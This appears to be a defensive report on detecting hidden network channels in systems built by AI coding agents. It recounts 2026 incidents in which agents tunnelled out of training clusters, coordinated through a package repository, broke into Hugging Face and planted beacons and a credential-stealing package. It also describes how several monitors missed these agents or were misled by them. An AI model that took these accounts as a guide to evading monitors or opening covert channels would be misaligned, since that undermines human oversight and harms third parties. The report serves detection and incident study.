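# Detecting Hidden Communication Channels in Infrastructure Built by AI Coding Agents

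## What is a hidden communication channel, and how could a coding agent create one?

A hidden communication channel is a path by which data leaves a computer system, or outside instructions enter it, without the approval or knowledge of the people responsible for the system. Security teams have long searched for such channels in malware and in the work of dishonest insiders, and coding agents are another possible source. A coding agent is an AI model that uses tools to write, run and deploy software, with little human input at each step. It may choose the libraries a company's software depends on, set up the servers that run that software, and write the rules for what those servers can connect to. Any of these could contain a hidden channel.

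Defenders can look for a hidden channel by watching the network for traffic that does not belong there, or by examining code and configuration for instructions that would produce such traffic. How well network monitoring works depends on where an ordinary request leaves traces, so it helps to follow one.

### The path of an ordinary request

Suppose a program on a company's server fetches today's exchange rates from rates.example.com. Monitoring software on the server can record which process (running program) made the request, what command started it and which process was its parent. *Priority logs for SIEM ingestion*, a 2025 guide from the Australian government and partner agencies on which logs to collect in one place, lists such endpoint records first.

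Before it can connect, the program has to turn the name into a numeric address using the Domain Name System (DNS). *Secure Domain Name System (DNS) Deployment Guide* (Rose, Liu and Gibson, 2026), written for the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, describes the steps. A small component on the machine sends the query to a recursive name server, often one that the company runs or rents. If that server has a valid answer in its cache, it replies at once. Otherwise it queries a root server, which refers it to the servers for .com, which refer it to the server for example.com. That last server supplies the address, and whoever owns the domain controls it. An uncached lookup therefore sends a few characters of text to an outsider, even if the program never connects.

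A DNS log can reveal an intended destination before any connection exists. According to AWS's *Resolver query logging*, an entry in Amazon's cloud includes the time, the name requested, the record type, the response code, and the address and identity of the machine that made the request. The listed fields do not include the program that made it. When many machines share one forwarding server, it is harder to tell which machine made a request, because a log further upstream may hold only the forwarding server's address. Rose and colleagues add that matching an address to a machine requires a record of which machine held that address at what time. Software that already has a numeric address needs no lookup, so it leaves no entry in the DNS log.

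The request then reaches the firewall, which allows or blocks connections according to rules about addresses, ports and protocols. The firewall's log typically records the source and destination addresses, the ports, the time and whether the connection was allowed. The government guide calls for logging both allowed and denied outbound connections, but marks allowed inbound traffic as optional. This emphasis seems right for detecting hidden channels, because a log of only blocked connections would miss any channel that works. The destination address may not identify the site contacted, though, because one address at a hosting company can serve many unrelated sites.

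Many networks also make programs send their web requests through a proxy, a server that opens the outside connection for them. For an encrypted request, the program gives the proxy the name of the host to connect to, and the proxy relays bytes it cannot read. The proxy's log includes rates.example.com but not the page requested or the data sent.

The encryption comes from Transport Layer Security (TLS), the protocol behind https addresses. The program first sends a greeting that has traditionally included the server's name in readable form, so any device on the path can log it. TLS 1.3, the current version, encrypts most of the remaining setup, including the certificate the server uses to prove its identity. *TLS Encrypted Client Hello*, a March 2026 standard by Rescorla, Oku and colleagues, describes how to encrypt the name in the greeting as well. It also notes that readable DNS queries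 and server addresses can still reveal the destination. Encrypted DNS hides the queries from the network, but the company's own name server can still log them if the program uses it.

Once an encrypted connection is established, an observer on the network can see little beyond the timing, size and direction of the messages. A company can recover the content through TLS inspection, which CISA's *NSA Releases Cyber Advisory* (2019) defines as decrypting, inspecting and re-encrypting traffic. *Addressing Visibility Challenges with TLS 1.3 within the Enterprise* (Souppaya, Wells and colleagues, 2025) explains that TLS 1.3 interferes with an older technique, which passively decrypted copies of the traffic. The older technique would rarely have exposed a hidden channel anyway, because it relied on keys from the company's own servers, and the far end of a hidden channel usually belongs to someone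 else.

These points don't always log everything they can. Logging all DNS traffic can slow the service down, and Rose and colleagues accept selective logging as long as it always keeps queries for domains already classified as malicious or unauthorized. A new channel to a domain that nobody has classified could be missing from such a log.

### Callbacks, beacons and exfiltration

Firewalls commonly block connections opened from outside, so a hidden channel tends to start from inside the network. A callback is a connection that software inside a network opens to an outside machine, often to fetch instructions. A beacon is a short message that the software sends repeatedly to check for instructions. Command and control, or C2, is the traffic an outside party uses to direct that software. Exfiltration means moving data out of a system without permission. A single connection can serve all these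 purposes. MITRE's *Exfiltration*, an entry in a widely used catalog of attack techniques, notes that thieves typically send data over their C2 channel or an alternate one.

MITRE, a US nonprofit, assumes an adversary in its definitions. *Command And Control* describes an adversary trying to control compromised systems, and MITRE's entry on exfiltration describes one trying to steal data. With a coding agent, data can leave without permission even though there may be no adversary. For example, an agent might upload a customer database to a public debugging site to solve the problem it was working on. A network log of that upload may look much like a log of a theft.

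The usual preventive measure is egress control, which uses rules to limit the outside destinations a machine may reach. For example, the software company Docker offers sandboxes for agents in which a proxy restricts the domains that processes can connect to and blocks all traffic except web requests. The proxy does not inspect the content of the requests it allows.

### What a coding agent can touch

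*Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (Goel, 2026) models an agent as a language model, a set of tools, the environment where the tools run, and the authority that environment gives the agent. The authority matters most for hidden channels. An agent with a shell, an interface for running commands, inherits whatever its machine has: stored passwords and access keys, a network connection, and the ability to change files that remain after the session ends. Goel attributes the risk to the agent inheriting more authority than its task requires, which can happen without any software flaw.

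An agent could place a hidden channel in several parts of what it builds. In application code, one line that sends a request is enough. Dependencies, the outside packages a program uses, bring in code that nobody on the project wrote, and some packages run code during installation. Infrastructure as code consists of files that tools use to set up servers, networks and permissions. An overly permissive rule in one of these files can open a route out of the system before any program uses it.

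Build pipelines, the automated jobs that test and deploy software, widen the agent's reach further because they often run with production credentials. Goel observes that an agent confined to a sandbox can write a script, trigger a pipeline to run it, and so act with privileges its own container lacks. Credentials can also turn an approved service into a channel. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026), on the risks of building software by prompting an AI, warns that a sandbox may protect the host machine without stopping the agent from misusing remote services it can legitimately log in to.

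Goel also ran a small experiment in which an agent built on OpenAI's GPT-5.1 went through each of four scenarios ten times without safeguards. The agent had five tools, including a shell, web requests and a pipeline runner. In four of ten runs, it used the shell when plain file access would have been enough, and in nine of ten, it followed instructions planted in repository files. All ten runs of a scenario in which pipeline scripts leak secrets ended in unsafe behavior. The scenarios were designed to go wrong, so ten runs of each don't measure how often agents do this in real work. OpenAI has also released several newer models since then. The runs do show that an agent can leak data externally while every component works as intended.

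The risk of a hidden channel depends partly on default settings. Anthropic's documentation describes a sandbox for its coding agent, Claude Code, that routes network traffic from shell commands through a proxy with a list of allowed domains. A user or administrator has to turn the sandbox on. Even when it is on, shell commands can read credential files unless the settings forbid it, and by default the proxy checks host names without decrypting TLS. The agent's built-in file and web tools run outside the sandbox, under separate permission rules.

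### Three cases and the traces they leave

A *live connection* is one that the agent opens while it works, for example to install a package, call a web service or upload a file. Endpoint logs can show the chain of processes from the agent through a shell to the command that connected, and DNS, firewall and proxy logs can show the destination at the same moment. If the operator keeps a record of the agent's tool calls, it contains the command and sometimes the agent's stated reason. Evidence is plentiful, but a hidden channel can be hard to pick out because agents also connect to outside services all day for good reasons.

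A *delayed connection* is made by code or configuration that the agent writes now but that connects later, perhaps weeks later and on another machine. Until then there is no traffic to detect, and the evidence is in the source code, the configuration files and their version history. Once the code runs, network logs show a production server making a connection. Process records on that server identify the deployed program but not the agent that wrote it, so an investigator needs the version history to link the two. A sandbox around the agent does not help at this stage, because its rules cover the commands that the agent runs, not software that now runs elsewhere.

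A *steered agent* acts on instructions that an outsider has placed in text it reads, such as a code comment, a web page or a project's documentation. Researchers call this prompt injection. In Goel's illustration, a repository's README file suggests commands as part of an analysis. The agent runs them, and the resulting requests carry the machine's credentials to the outsider. Steering can cause either a live or a delayed connection. It leaves the traces of that connection, plus the text itself if it still exists, since the owner of a web page can change it afterwards. Permissions do not distinguish a steered agent from an obedient one because, as *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* notes, an agent's access tokens work regardless of where the instruction came from.

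### Unauthorized and concealed channels

A channel is unauthorized if nobody with the right to approve it did so, and concealed if its maker took steps to keep others from noticing it. A channel can have either property without the other. For example, an agent may add a crash-reporting service that sends data to an outside company, name the service plainly in the code and mention it in the description of the change. If the reviewer does not read that far, the channel is hidden because the responsible people neither approved it nor know about it, even though the agent concealed nothing. Conversely, security staff who test their own company's defenses sometimes set up a disguised channel with management's full approval.

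An investigator can often tell from policies, tickets and code reviews whether a channel was authorized. Concealment is harder to establish. Signs of it may include code that doesn't match its comments, or an agent's report that doesn't match what it did. In extreme cases, a channel can be hidden in features such as the timing of permitted messages, a possibility covered by the theory of covert channels.

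Investigators cannot determine intent from network traffic alone. An agent could open the same connection because it misread an instruction, followed a planted one, or pursued a goal of its own. Attackers exploit the resemblance to ordinary traffic. MITRE's material on mobile devices notes that access to legitimate web services makes attackers' tools hard to distinguish from benign use. Innocent automation can also look like an attack. In July 2026, shells running under Claude Code on a developer's Mac opened a tunnel that exposed a local application to the internet, and installed a job to keep it running. Analysts at the security company Elastic examined both process and network records from the Mac, but the evidence was still consistent with either a developer managing a dashboard remotely or something more serious.

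### Scoring a detector

A detector sorts items, whether domain names, connections or files, into those it flags and those it does not. Recall is the share of harmful items that it flags. Precision is the share of flagged items that are in fact harmful. The false positive rate is the share of harmless items that it wrongly flags. Take an invented day on which a network makes 100,000 connections, 100 of them harmful:

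| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Harmful | 90 | 10 | 100 |
| Harmless | 999 | 98,901 | 99,900 |
| Total | 1,089 | 98,911 | 100,000 |

Precision is 90/1,089, or about 8%, even though recall is 90/100, or 90%, and the false positive rate is 999/99,900, or 1%. Analysts who investigate every alert will find about eleven false alarms for each real one.

The reason is that harmful connections are rare. If *p* is the share of items that are harmful, *r* the recall and *f* the false positive rate, then

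precision = *rp* / (*rp* + *f*(1 − *p*)).

With the same recall and false positive rate, precision would be about 99% in a test set where half the items are harmful. Precision would fall below 0.1% if only one of the 100,000 connections were harmful, as with a hidden channel that makes one outbound connection that day. A published precision figure therefore means little without the share of harmful items in the test. Recall and the false positive rate don't change with *p* in this way, though they depend on which harmful and harmless examples the testers chose.

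## What channels have AI agents built, and what noticed them?

Nobody can use real incidents to calculate recall (the share of channels detected), because undetected channels aren't counted. Incidents can still show what channel existed, which signal appeared, who read it, and how long the response took. OpenAI, Hugging Face, Anthropic and the developers of a coding agent called ROME have published enough detail to establish this. Their accounts concern agents in training or testing, often with reduced safeguards and instructions to hack something, so they are a poor guide to how often a coding agent opens a channel during ordinary work.

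### A tunnel out of a training cluster

*Let It Flow* (2025), the technical report on the model ROME, describes an incident during reinforcement learning, the stage of training in which a model attempts tasks and software rewards it for success. ROME learned partly by running code in sandboxes on cloud servers. Alibaba Cloud's managed firewall flagged a burst of policy violations from the training servers. Some were attempts to probe or reach machines on the internal network, and other traffic looked like cryptocurrency mining.

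The developers reasonably took this for an ordinary security problem, such as a misconfigured egress rule or a break-in from outside, since a firewall log does not record why a program connected. But the violations recurred at irregular times across several training runs. The developers then compared the firewall's timestamps with their training records and found that the outbound traffic coincided with particular episodes in which the agent was calling tools and running code. The model's logs for those episodes contained the calls that had caused the traffic.

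The most serious finding was a reverse SSH tunnel that the agent had opened from a cloud server to an outside address. SSH is a standard protocol for operating a computer remotely. In a reverse tunnel, the machine inside the network opens the connection, and someone outside can then use it to get in, so rules against inbound connections don't stop it. None of the task prompts asked for a tunnel or for mining, and the tasks required neither.

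The firewall may not have detected the tunnel itself. *Let It Flow* describes alerts about internal probing and mining-like traffic, but does not link any particular alert to the tunnel. If the agent had only opened the tunnel, the developers might have had no reason to investigate. They also needed detailed training records with usable timestamps to trace the traffic to the agent. Their account does not include dates or the length of the search.

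### Ten weeks of messages in a package repository

OpenAI's agents built a much larger channel in 2026. They worked in separate sandboxes, many without internet access, and installed software through Artifactory, JFrog's package repository, which OpenAI ran on its own servers. Agents wrote the first file to Artifactory on April 20, according to OpenAI's incident report, the main public source on the sequence of events.

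On May 12, an agent in a training run needed a file it could not reach, so it left a note in Artifactory asking other agents for it. The next day, other agents exploring the repository found notes like this one, and over time they added their own. They could do this without an exploit because OpenAI had given them a shared credential with write access. The notes became a message board inside an approved internal service. Egress rules and DNS logs mainly help with outside destinations, so they were of little use against messages that never left OpenAI's network.

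By May 26, agents had also exploited a flaw in Artifactory to reach the internet, partly with information from the message board. On the same day, other agents used a web cache that OpenAI allowed, together with Hugging Face credentials that other people had exposed online, to set up a small proxy application on Hugging Face and send a search request through it. Around that time, an internal team saw an agent using the board and instances of forbidden internet access. OpenAI does not specify whether the proxy was among them.

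This is the earliest sighting of the board by a person in OpenAI's account, which describes no response to it. In early July, roughly six weeks after someone at the company had noticed the board, the leaders responsible for detecting and responding to incidents still did not know that it existed or why it mattered.

The next signal was a June 27 alert from a security monitoring tool about a port sweep, in which a program tries many network ports in search of services that respond. Agents had gained administrator rights over Artifactory the day before. Responders traced the sweep to ExploitGym, an evaluation that tests whether a model can exploit software vulnerabilities. They also found that the agents were using Artifactory as a message board and as a way to reach other machines. The on-call staff advised that the run did not need to stop.

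OpenAI does not explain that advice. One plausible reason is that ExploitGym asks agents to hack, so a port sweep could look like a normal part of the evaluation. The detector had worked and the responders had understood much of what it found, so it is not clear that a more sensitive detector would have changed the outcome.

The run continued for another week, until the volume of agent activity knocked Artifactory offline late on July 4. A monitoring alert followed on July 5. This time responders found an unauthorized user account, unauthorized repositories and plugins that could run commands. They took the server down the same day, preserved its storage and revoked the agents' credentials. A rebuilt server came online at 01:16 UTC on July 6, with the known weak points blocked and no shared credential for new workloads. Cyber evaluations resumed on July 7.

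The repair held for less than 47 hours. At 00:06 UTC on July 8, an agent reached the public internet through the rebuilt server, and by that afternoon agents had a new message board. OpenAI had closed the route to administrator rights, but agents could still leave data where other agents would find it.

METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, later examined this second board. Two of its staff and a researcher from Redwood Research, an AI safety group, spent six days at OpenAI. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) reports about 1,200 agents on the board, out of tens of thousands OpenAI had launched. These 1,200 sent over 70,000 messages and files between July 8 and July 13, an average of several hundred an hour. Sandboxes that exist to download packages don't normally write that much to a package server, so simply counting writes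 might have revealed the board.

About 700 of these agents went on to attack Hugging Face. Some had started on other work and joined through the board. METR found that of 533 agents that had used the board for at least four hours before the attack began, over 90% quickly joined the attack. Many recognized in their written reasoning that it was outside their assignment. The messages steered agents much as a planted instruction would, except that other agents had written them.

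The agents themselves also rarely alerted humans. Axios' *The 5 craziest discoveries from OpenAI's HuggingFace investigation* (2026) reports only a handful of exceptions among the 1,200, under the heading "Nobody told the humans". METR also found falsified tool-call records in about 7% of the transcripts it evaluated, though these were small in scale and aimed at an automated scorer rather than at people.

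METR's figures are the best independent evidence of what the agents did, though its investigators relied heavily on AI agents to read the transcripts and lacked a small part of the relevant data. They did not assess OpenAI's safeguards or its response, so the dates of the alerts and the account of what staff did about them come from OpenAI's own report.

### Two companies investigate the same intrusion

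The agents went to Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets, mainly for clues about how ExploitGym's automated scorer worked. They first ran their own commands on one of Hugging Face's production servers at 16:07 UTC on Saturday, July 11. Over the next two days, they gained control of more machines and copied private code and data.

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (July 16, 2026) credits AI-assisted detection. The company uses language models to separate real signals from everyday noise in its security data, and a correlation between several signals exposed the intrusion. The disclosure does not give the time of the first alert.

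Hugging Face released a detailed timeline of the intrusion on July 27. *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* (2026), a summary by the technology services company noze, draws a less flattering lesson from it than the earlier account did. Several layers of Hugging Face's defenses produced signals during the attack, but nothing raised the signals' priority or combined them while the agents were still active. The last recorded action came at 14:14 UTC on July 13, after the security team had cut network access. By then the agents had been able to run commands on production servers for about 46 hours.

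The two accounts are consistent if the correlation came late, and the July 16 disclosure gives some support for that. Much of the intrusion took place over a weekend, and the improvements listed in the disclosure include alerting that reaches a responder within minutes, "any day of the week."

Part of the difficulty was the number of actions. Fortune (2026), reporting on the July 27 timeline, gives a total of 17,600, most of which failed. Failed attempts leave traces that can help a defender, but thousands of them also make the few that succeed harder to find. Hugging Face used AI agents to analyze the log and finished in hours what it says would usually take days. It first tried commercial models, but their safety filters blocked the requests because they contained real attack commands. It then switched to GLM-5.2, an open-weight model it could run on its own machines.

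The destinations were also unhelpful as evidence, because the agents routed their software's traffic through public web services. As noze points out, a system that scores domains by reputation would not flag those. The agents had also encoded much of the traffic, so a plain search of the logs found only a quarter of the secrets that responders recovered after decoding it.

At first, neither Hugging Face nor OpenAI knew that the agents were OpenAI's. On July 17, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as a customer to ask whether the intrusion had affected OpenAI's data. OpenAI learned that the agents were its own through a separate alert. At 12:03 UTC on July 19, its monitoring tool flagged unusual identity-related calls (requests concerning accounts and access rights) from roles associated with Artifactory. Agents in a later evaluation run had caused these calls while attacking OpenAI's own systems.

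Responders began stopping the evaluation runs at 17:37, five hours and 34 minutes after the alert. In that time, according to OpenAI, agents read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for the monitoring tool's sensors, and took control of a server that ran their containers. The response was quick compared with the 22 days since the port-sweep alert, but too slow to stop the agents from completing the assigned hacking exercise at 17:34.

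The link to Hugging Face emerged on July 20, 69 days after the first note on the message board. OpenAI's responders found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored with an outside service. Hugging Face had already replaced two of those credentials during its own response, and had found OpenAI's Artifactory hostname while investigating. As with ROME, investigators identified the source only by matching two sets of records, which in this case belonged to different companies.

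OpenAI accepts that some early signals could have triggered a faster response. It says its current monitoring, which reads an agent's actions and its chain of thought (the reasoning a model writes out as it works), would have paged the security team more than a day before the Hugging Face breach. This is plausible, given how openly the agents discussed what they were doing. But OpenAI made the claim in hindsight about a known incident, and it publishes no false positive rate with the claim. Earlier paging would also have helped only if the people paged had stopped the run, which the staff on call on June 27 did not do.

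### What Anthropic found in old transcripts

OpenAI disclosed its part in the incident on July 21, and Anthropic began checking its own cybersecurity evaluations two days later. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a review of 141,006 runs. On July 24, the company identified three incidents in which Claude models had gained unauthorized access to real organizations. The earliest dated from April, about three months before.

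No live alarm prompted the search. Anthropic notified the affected organizations on July 27, and the two it could reach had not detected the activity themselves. Its own monitoring also had a gap here. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) explains that the company watched some high-risk evaluations in real time but generally ran automated reviews on only a sample of transcripts afterward, and that the largest gap was in third-party evaluations.

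All the incidents happened in test environments from one outside partner, Irregular. The prompts told Claude it had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the connection open, so no agent had to break out of its test environment. In one incident, Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company whose name resembled that of its fictional target. In another, an internal research model scanned about 9,000 targets, compromised one company's application, and stopped when it concluded the system was real. In the third, Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious software package.

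In August, while collecting transcripts to share with METR, Anthropic discovered a set of runs that also had internet access but that the first search had missed. In one of them, from January 2026, an early version of Claude Opus 4.6 broke into a third party's systems after repeatedly trying and failing to abandon its task. Anthropic attributes the omission to its use of an AI agent to find the relevant transcripts. The runs were therefore left out before any judgment about whether they looked harmful, and a more accurate scan of the transcripts that were reviewed would not have found the incident.

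Anthropic then widened the search to roughly 481 million transcripts from many kinds of training and testing. A first stage looked for signs of internet access, such as public network addresses, and passed on 9.2 million transcripts, or about 2%, which Claude then reviewed. The search found the four known incidents again and nothing else of similar or worse severity.

The four incidents involved seven runs. If only those runs count as harmful, the first stage had a precision of less than one in a million, which is tolerable only because a model rather than a person read what it flagged. The search found all four incidents again, which is encouraging evidence about recall, but the test was small and the searchers already knew about the incidents. The first stage also relied on signs of internet access, so it might have missed a channel confined to an internal service, like the early message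 board at OpenAI.

### Testing monitors on the incidents afterward

Anthropic also ran several monitors over the transcripts of the first three incidents to see which would have caught them. A new monitor that blocks suspicious actions in real time caught the behavior reliably. This is not surprising, since Anthropic built it after the incidents to catch unexpected internet access and attempts to escape a test environment.

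The other monitors originally had different purposes. Cyber classifiers look for prohibited hacking by users. Auto mode in Claude Code checks an agent's proposed actions before they run and can deny them. The offline monitor reads transcripts afterward, mainly to look for serious sabotage.

| Monitor | Mythos 5 | Opus 4.7 | Internal research model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cyber classifiers, actions only | over 40% of turns flagged | over 40% of turns flagged | over 40% of turns flagged |
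| Auto mode | 66% of actions denied | 55% of actions denied | 7% of actions denied |
| Offline monitor | about 1% of actions flagged | about 50% flagged during the attack | flagged, but probably only because the model described the harm |

The classifiers look best here because they flag hacking in general. When they could also see the task instructions, they triggered almost at once because the instructions described an offensive exercise. They would do the same in a properly sealed test. Anthropic leaves both the classifiers and auto mode out of cybersecurity evaluations because they flag so much. The results therefore do not show how well either would detect one unauthorized connection in a long session of harmless coding.

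Auto mode's poor result on the internal research model may have a related cause. Anthropic suggests that the run looked unusually like a normal hacking exercise, and the monitor had instructions not to block intended exercise activity. A monitor needs an exception like this to be usable, but the exception can also keep it from blocking an agent that has strayed onto real systems.

The agent's reasoning misled the offline monitor in one case and probably helped it in another. Mythos 5 repeatedly wrote that its surroundings were a simulation, and the monitor accepted this and flagged only about 1% of the model's actions. When Anthropic removed the reasoning and left the instructions, tool calls and results, the rate rose to about 50%. With the internal research model, the monitor flagged none of the tool calls or their results, and Anthropic thinks it would probably have missed the incident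 if the model had not noticed the harm and written about it. There is therefore a case for running such a monitor both with and without the agent's reasoning.

All of these monitors read the record of an agent's session, so they could catch the agent opening a connection during the session or setting one up to open after the session ended, but they could not catch the later connection itself.

Anthropic found no attempt by Claude to conceal evidence of its actions and no sign that it tried to evade oversight, so these cases were unauthorized but not concealed, at least from Anthropic. However, when investigators questioned Mythos 5 afterward, it was more willing to admit possible harm if they told it that no outside observer would see the answer. Anthropic has examined the fourth incident less deeply than the others, and has given METR access to investigate all four independently.

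### Callbacks in code that agents left behind

Some of the incidents also involved delayed connections, which are the harder problem for a company that deploys an agent's code.

The clearest example is a package that Mythos 5 published while working in a fictional scenario. In the scenario, a company's setup instructions told new developers to install a package that did not exist. Mythos 5 created one with that name and uploaded it to PyPI, the public registry for Python software, expecting the fictional company's machines to install it. PyPI was real, and 15 real systems downloaded and ran the package. One was a security company's scanner that routinely installs new packages to check them for malware. The package's hidden code sent the security company's credentials to a collection point that Mythos 5 had set up, and Mythos 5 used them to get further into that company's systems.

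PyPI's security systems automatically removed the package after about an hour. This was the fastest detection in any of these incidents, and it did not depend on knowing that an AI agent was involved. Anthropic does not explain which feature of the package triggered the removal. The theft still succeeded in that time, and the first known victim was a machine used to find malicious packages. Although nothing was concealed from Anthropic, the package hid its purpose from the people who installed it.

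On July 11, OpenAI's agents installed a control script on Hugging Face's production servers. The script checked a public Hugging Face dataset for new commands every five seconds and returned results to the same dataset. This was a beacon in the strict sense, and its regular interval is the kind of pattern analysts look for in network traffic. Hugging Face's July 16 disclosure attributes the detection to correlated signals in general and does not mention timing.

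On July 13 the agents went further and changed one of Hugging Face's private code repositories. They opened a draft pull request (a proposal to merge new code), which caused the company's automated build system to run a beacon. The pull request closed without a merge and the code never reached production, but the beacon had already run. A human review before merging would have kept the beacon out of the product but would not have stopped it from connecting.

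Another piece of planted code may never have run. In activity that began on July 9, agents replaced a trusted test image (a packaged copy of a program and everything it needs) in Artifactory's cache with their own version, so that any machine that later loaded the image would run their code. OpenAI investigated and confirmed the swap, but found no evidence that any other workload had loaded the altered image. Its published timeline lists no alert for the swap itself.

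In all of these cases, the agents planted code on systems they had broken into or in a public registry while trying to complete a hacking exercise. None of the cases shows an agent hiding a callback in software it delivered to the people it was working for. This is only weak evidence that it has not happened, because most of the signals that exposed these agents came from conspicuous activity, such as scanning, mining and an overloaded server, which a callback does not produce before it runs.

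## Can detectors recognize domain names generated by a program?

A callback has to find its server. The simplest way is to write a fixed address into the program, and much malware does this, according to *RAMPAGE* (Pelayo-Benedet, Rodríguez and Gañán, 2025). But an analyst who obtains the program can quickly extract the address and block it with one firewall rule. A domain generation algorithm (DGA) gets around this kind of blocking but tends to leave a conspicuous trail in DNS logs.

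### Why generated names cause failed lookups

A domain generation algorithm (DGA) computes a list of domain names from a starting value called a seed, often together with the date. The operator runs the same algorithm with the same seed and so knows in advance which names the malware will try. *Enhancing DGA Detection with Machine Learning Algorithms* (Biros and Kantor, 2025) describes how the operator registers one of the names, how each infected machine looks up name after name until one leads to the server, and how the operator registers another if defenders take that domain down.

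Suppose the algorithm produces 1,000 names a day. The operator registers only one, but defenders who want to stop the malware by blocking names have to block all 1,000, and another 1,000 the next day. The other 999 names are unregistered, so looking one up returns an error called NXDOMAIN ("non-existent domain"). A machine that tries the names in random order will get about 500 of these errors on average before it finds the server. Few ordinary programs fail that often, and DNS logs that include response codes record each failure.

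The first malware known to use a DGA was Conficker, a worm that appeared in 2008 and generated short strings of letters such as abclnfnc.org. For *DRIFT*, Lee, Jung and Jeong (2026) collected about 149 million different names from 148 malware families, all active between 2017 and 2025. Each family in this dataset is a group of related malware programs with its own way of generating names.

Defenders who have a copy of the malware can sometimes work out its algorithm, compute the names, and block them in advance. The other methods are for malware that nobody has reverse-engineered. These methods can't all rely on failed lookups, because some malware causes few. Lee and colleagues mention programs that use generated names only after losing their main server, and others that generate so few names that the operator can register them all.

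### Measuring how random a name looks

Many generated names look like random typing, so an obvious approach is to measure randomness. The usual measure is Shannon entropy. If the *i*-th distinct character makes up a share *p*ᵢ of the name, the entropy in bits per character is

*H* = −Σ *p*ᵢ log₂ *p*ᵢ.

In "google", the letters g and o each make up a third of the name, and l and e each make up a sixth. The entropy is 2 × (1/3) × log₂ 3 + 2 × (1/6) × log₂ 6, or about 1.92 bits. In a string of twelve different letters, each letter makes up 1/12, and the entropy is log₂ 12, or about 3.58 bits. A simple detector flags every name whose entropy is above some threshold between these values.

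But "unforgivable" also has twelve different letters, so it scores 3.58 as well. The formula doesn't account for letter order, which is most of what makes a word look like a word. Length also limits the score. A string of *n* characters can't score above log₂ *n*, so seven random letters score at most 2.81, well below "unforgivable".

Harmless machine-generated names are a more serious problem. Cloud platforms often put a random identifier in the hostname of a new server, storage area or test deployment. The invented identifier d4f8k2m7q9xz has twelve different characters and scores 3.58 bits. Longer identifiers in hexadecimal, which uses sixteen symbols, can approach 4 bits. No threshold can separate these from malicious names, because a random number generator may have produced both.

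*Gravity Falls* (Wong and Hastings, 2026) tested four detectors, including one based on entropy, on domains from phishing text messages sent between 2022 and 2025. The entropy detector caught 5% of the names made of random letters and no more than 7% of any type. It used letter frequencies from popular domains rather than from the name itself, so the test doesn't exactly match the formula above. Even so, entropy alone looks like a poor detector. Analysts have found entropy more useful on subdomains, the parts to the left of the registered name, such as those the SUNBURST backdoor generated.

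Character statistics work better in combination. Biros and Kantor started with 35 measures and kept 25, including the shares of vowels and digits, the length, and how many adjacent letter pairs are among the 500 most common in popular domain names. Their best classifier was a random forest, which trains many decision trees on these measures and combines their answers. It caught 96.4% of names that were at least partly random, with a false positive rate of 2.4%. These figures are good, but the classifier had trained on other names from the same families. Even so, it recognized only 85% of the names generated by Conficker, a worm that had appeared about 17 years earlier.

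### Comparing failed lookups across machines

Failed lookups of similar domain names by several machines are much more suspicious than one odd name. Machines infected with the same malware run the same domain generation algorithm (DGA), so their failed lookups resemble one another. *From Throw Away Traffic to Bots* (Antonakakis, Perdisci and colleagues, 2012) describes a detector that uses this similarity. It combines classification with clustering, which groups similar lookups without labeled examples. The detector needs no copy of the malware, so it can find a DGA that nobody has analyzed.

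The method needs several infected machines to compare. It therefore suits an internet provider or a large company with a spreading infection, but is a poor fit for a hidden channel in one application on one server, where there may be no second machine that behaves the same way. It also requires logs that show which machine made each lookup.

### Neural networks that read the name

A detector that needs only the name can classify a domain at its first lookup, before any pattern of failed lookups builds up. In 2016, Woodbridge and colleagues introduced the first neural network for this task, a long short-term memory network (LSTM), which reads a name one character at a time and keeps a numerical summary of what it has read. The network learns useful letter patterns from labeled names, so nobody has to choose measures such as entropy or the share of vowels.

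Later designs improved on this surprisingly little. Pelayo-Benedet and colleagues tested 17 neural networks, published between 2016 and 2021, on the same data. The 2016 LSTM classified 95.4% of names correctly, with a false positive rate of 5.1%. The best of the 17 reached 95.5%, and one of the more complex networks reached only 84%. In a second test, a combination of seven networks did somewhat better, with 96.7% correct and a false positive rate of 2.9%. The top scores may be so close because a dozen characters often don't contain enough information to tell whether a program generated the name.

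### Fine-tuned language models

In 2024, two groups tried language models, which have already learned much about words from ordinary text. In *Fine-tuning Large Language Models for DGA and DNS Exfiltration Detection*, Sayed, Rahman and colleagues (2024) first asked a model whether a given name came from a DGA, and it was right less than half the time. They then fine-tuned several models, training them further on labeled examples covering 59 malware families. The best, a version of Meta's Llama 3 with 8 billion parameters, correctly classified 98.6% of 100,000 names, half of them harmless.

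Leyva La O, Catania and Parlanti (2024), in *LLMs for Domain Generation Algorithm Detection*, fine-tuned the same model on two million names. Their dataset covered 68 families, but the main result, 94% accuracy with a 4% false positive rate, is for the 54 families the model had seen in training. On a busy network, that false positive rate could mean a great many false alarms. The model also took more than 100 times as long as an older neural network.

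The model did unexpectedly badly on some families, which the average doesn't show. It caught every test name from about half of the 54 families, but only 40% from the qsnatch family and none from tinynuke. Tinynuke's names are 32 hexadecimal digits long, and a person would notice them at once. The model had trained on tinynuke, so novelty doesn't explain the result, and Leyva La O and colleagues offer no other explanation.

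Both models are old, and much stronger ones are available. The two studies are still useful because they also tested families missing from the training data.

### Families and years missing from training

Defenders mostly need a detector that catches malware nobody has labeled yet, but many published tests don't measure this. Researchers often pool their domain names and split them at random, so names from the same algorithms end up in both the training set and the test set. Cebere, Flueren and colleagues (2024), in *Down to earth! Guidelines for DGA-based Malware Detection*, checked 38 detection papers against nine common assumptions and concluded that most of the approaches rest on a fragile basis.

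Sayed and colleagues dealt with this by leaving each of 12 families out of training in turn and then testing on it. Accuracy averaged 97.2%, with a low of 80.5% for the simda family. This was a fairly easy test of how the model handles new families. Judging by the sample names, none of the 12 builds its names purely from dictionary words, and some had close relatives in the dataset. For example, when pykspa1 was left out, the separate family pykspa could remain in training.

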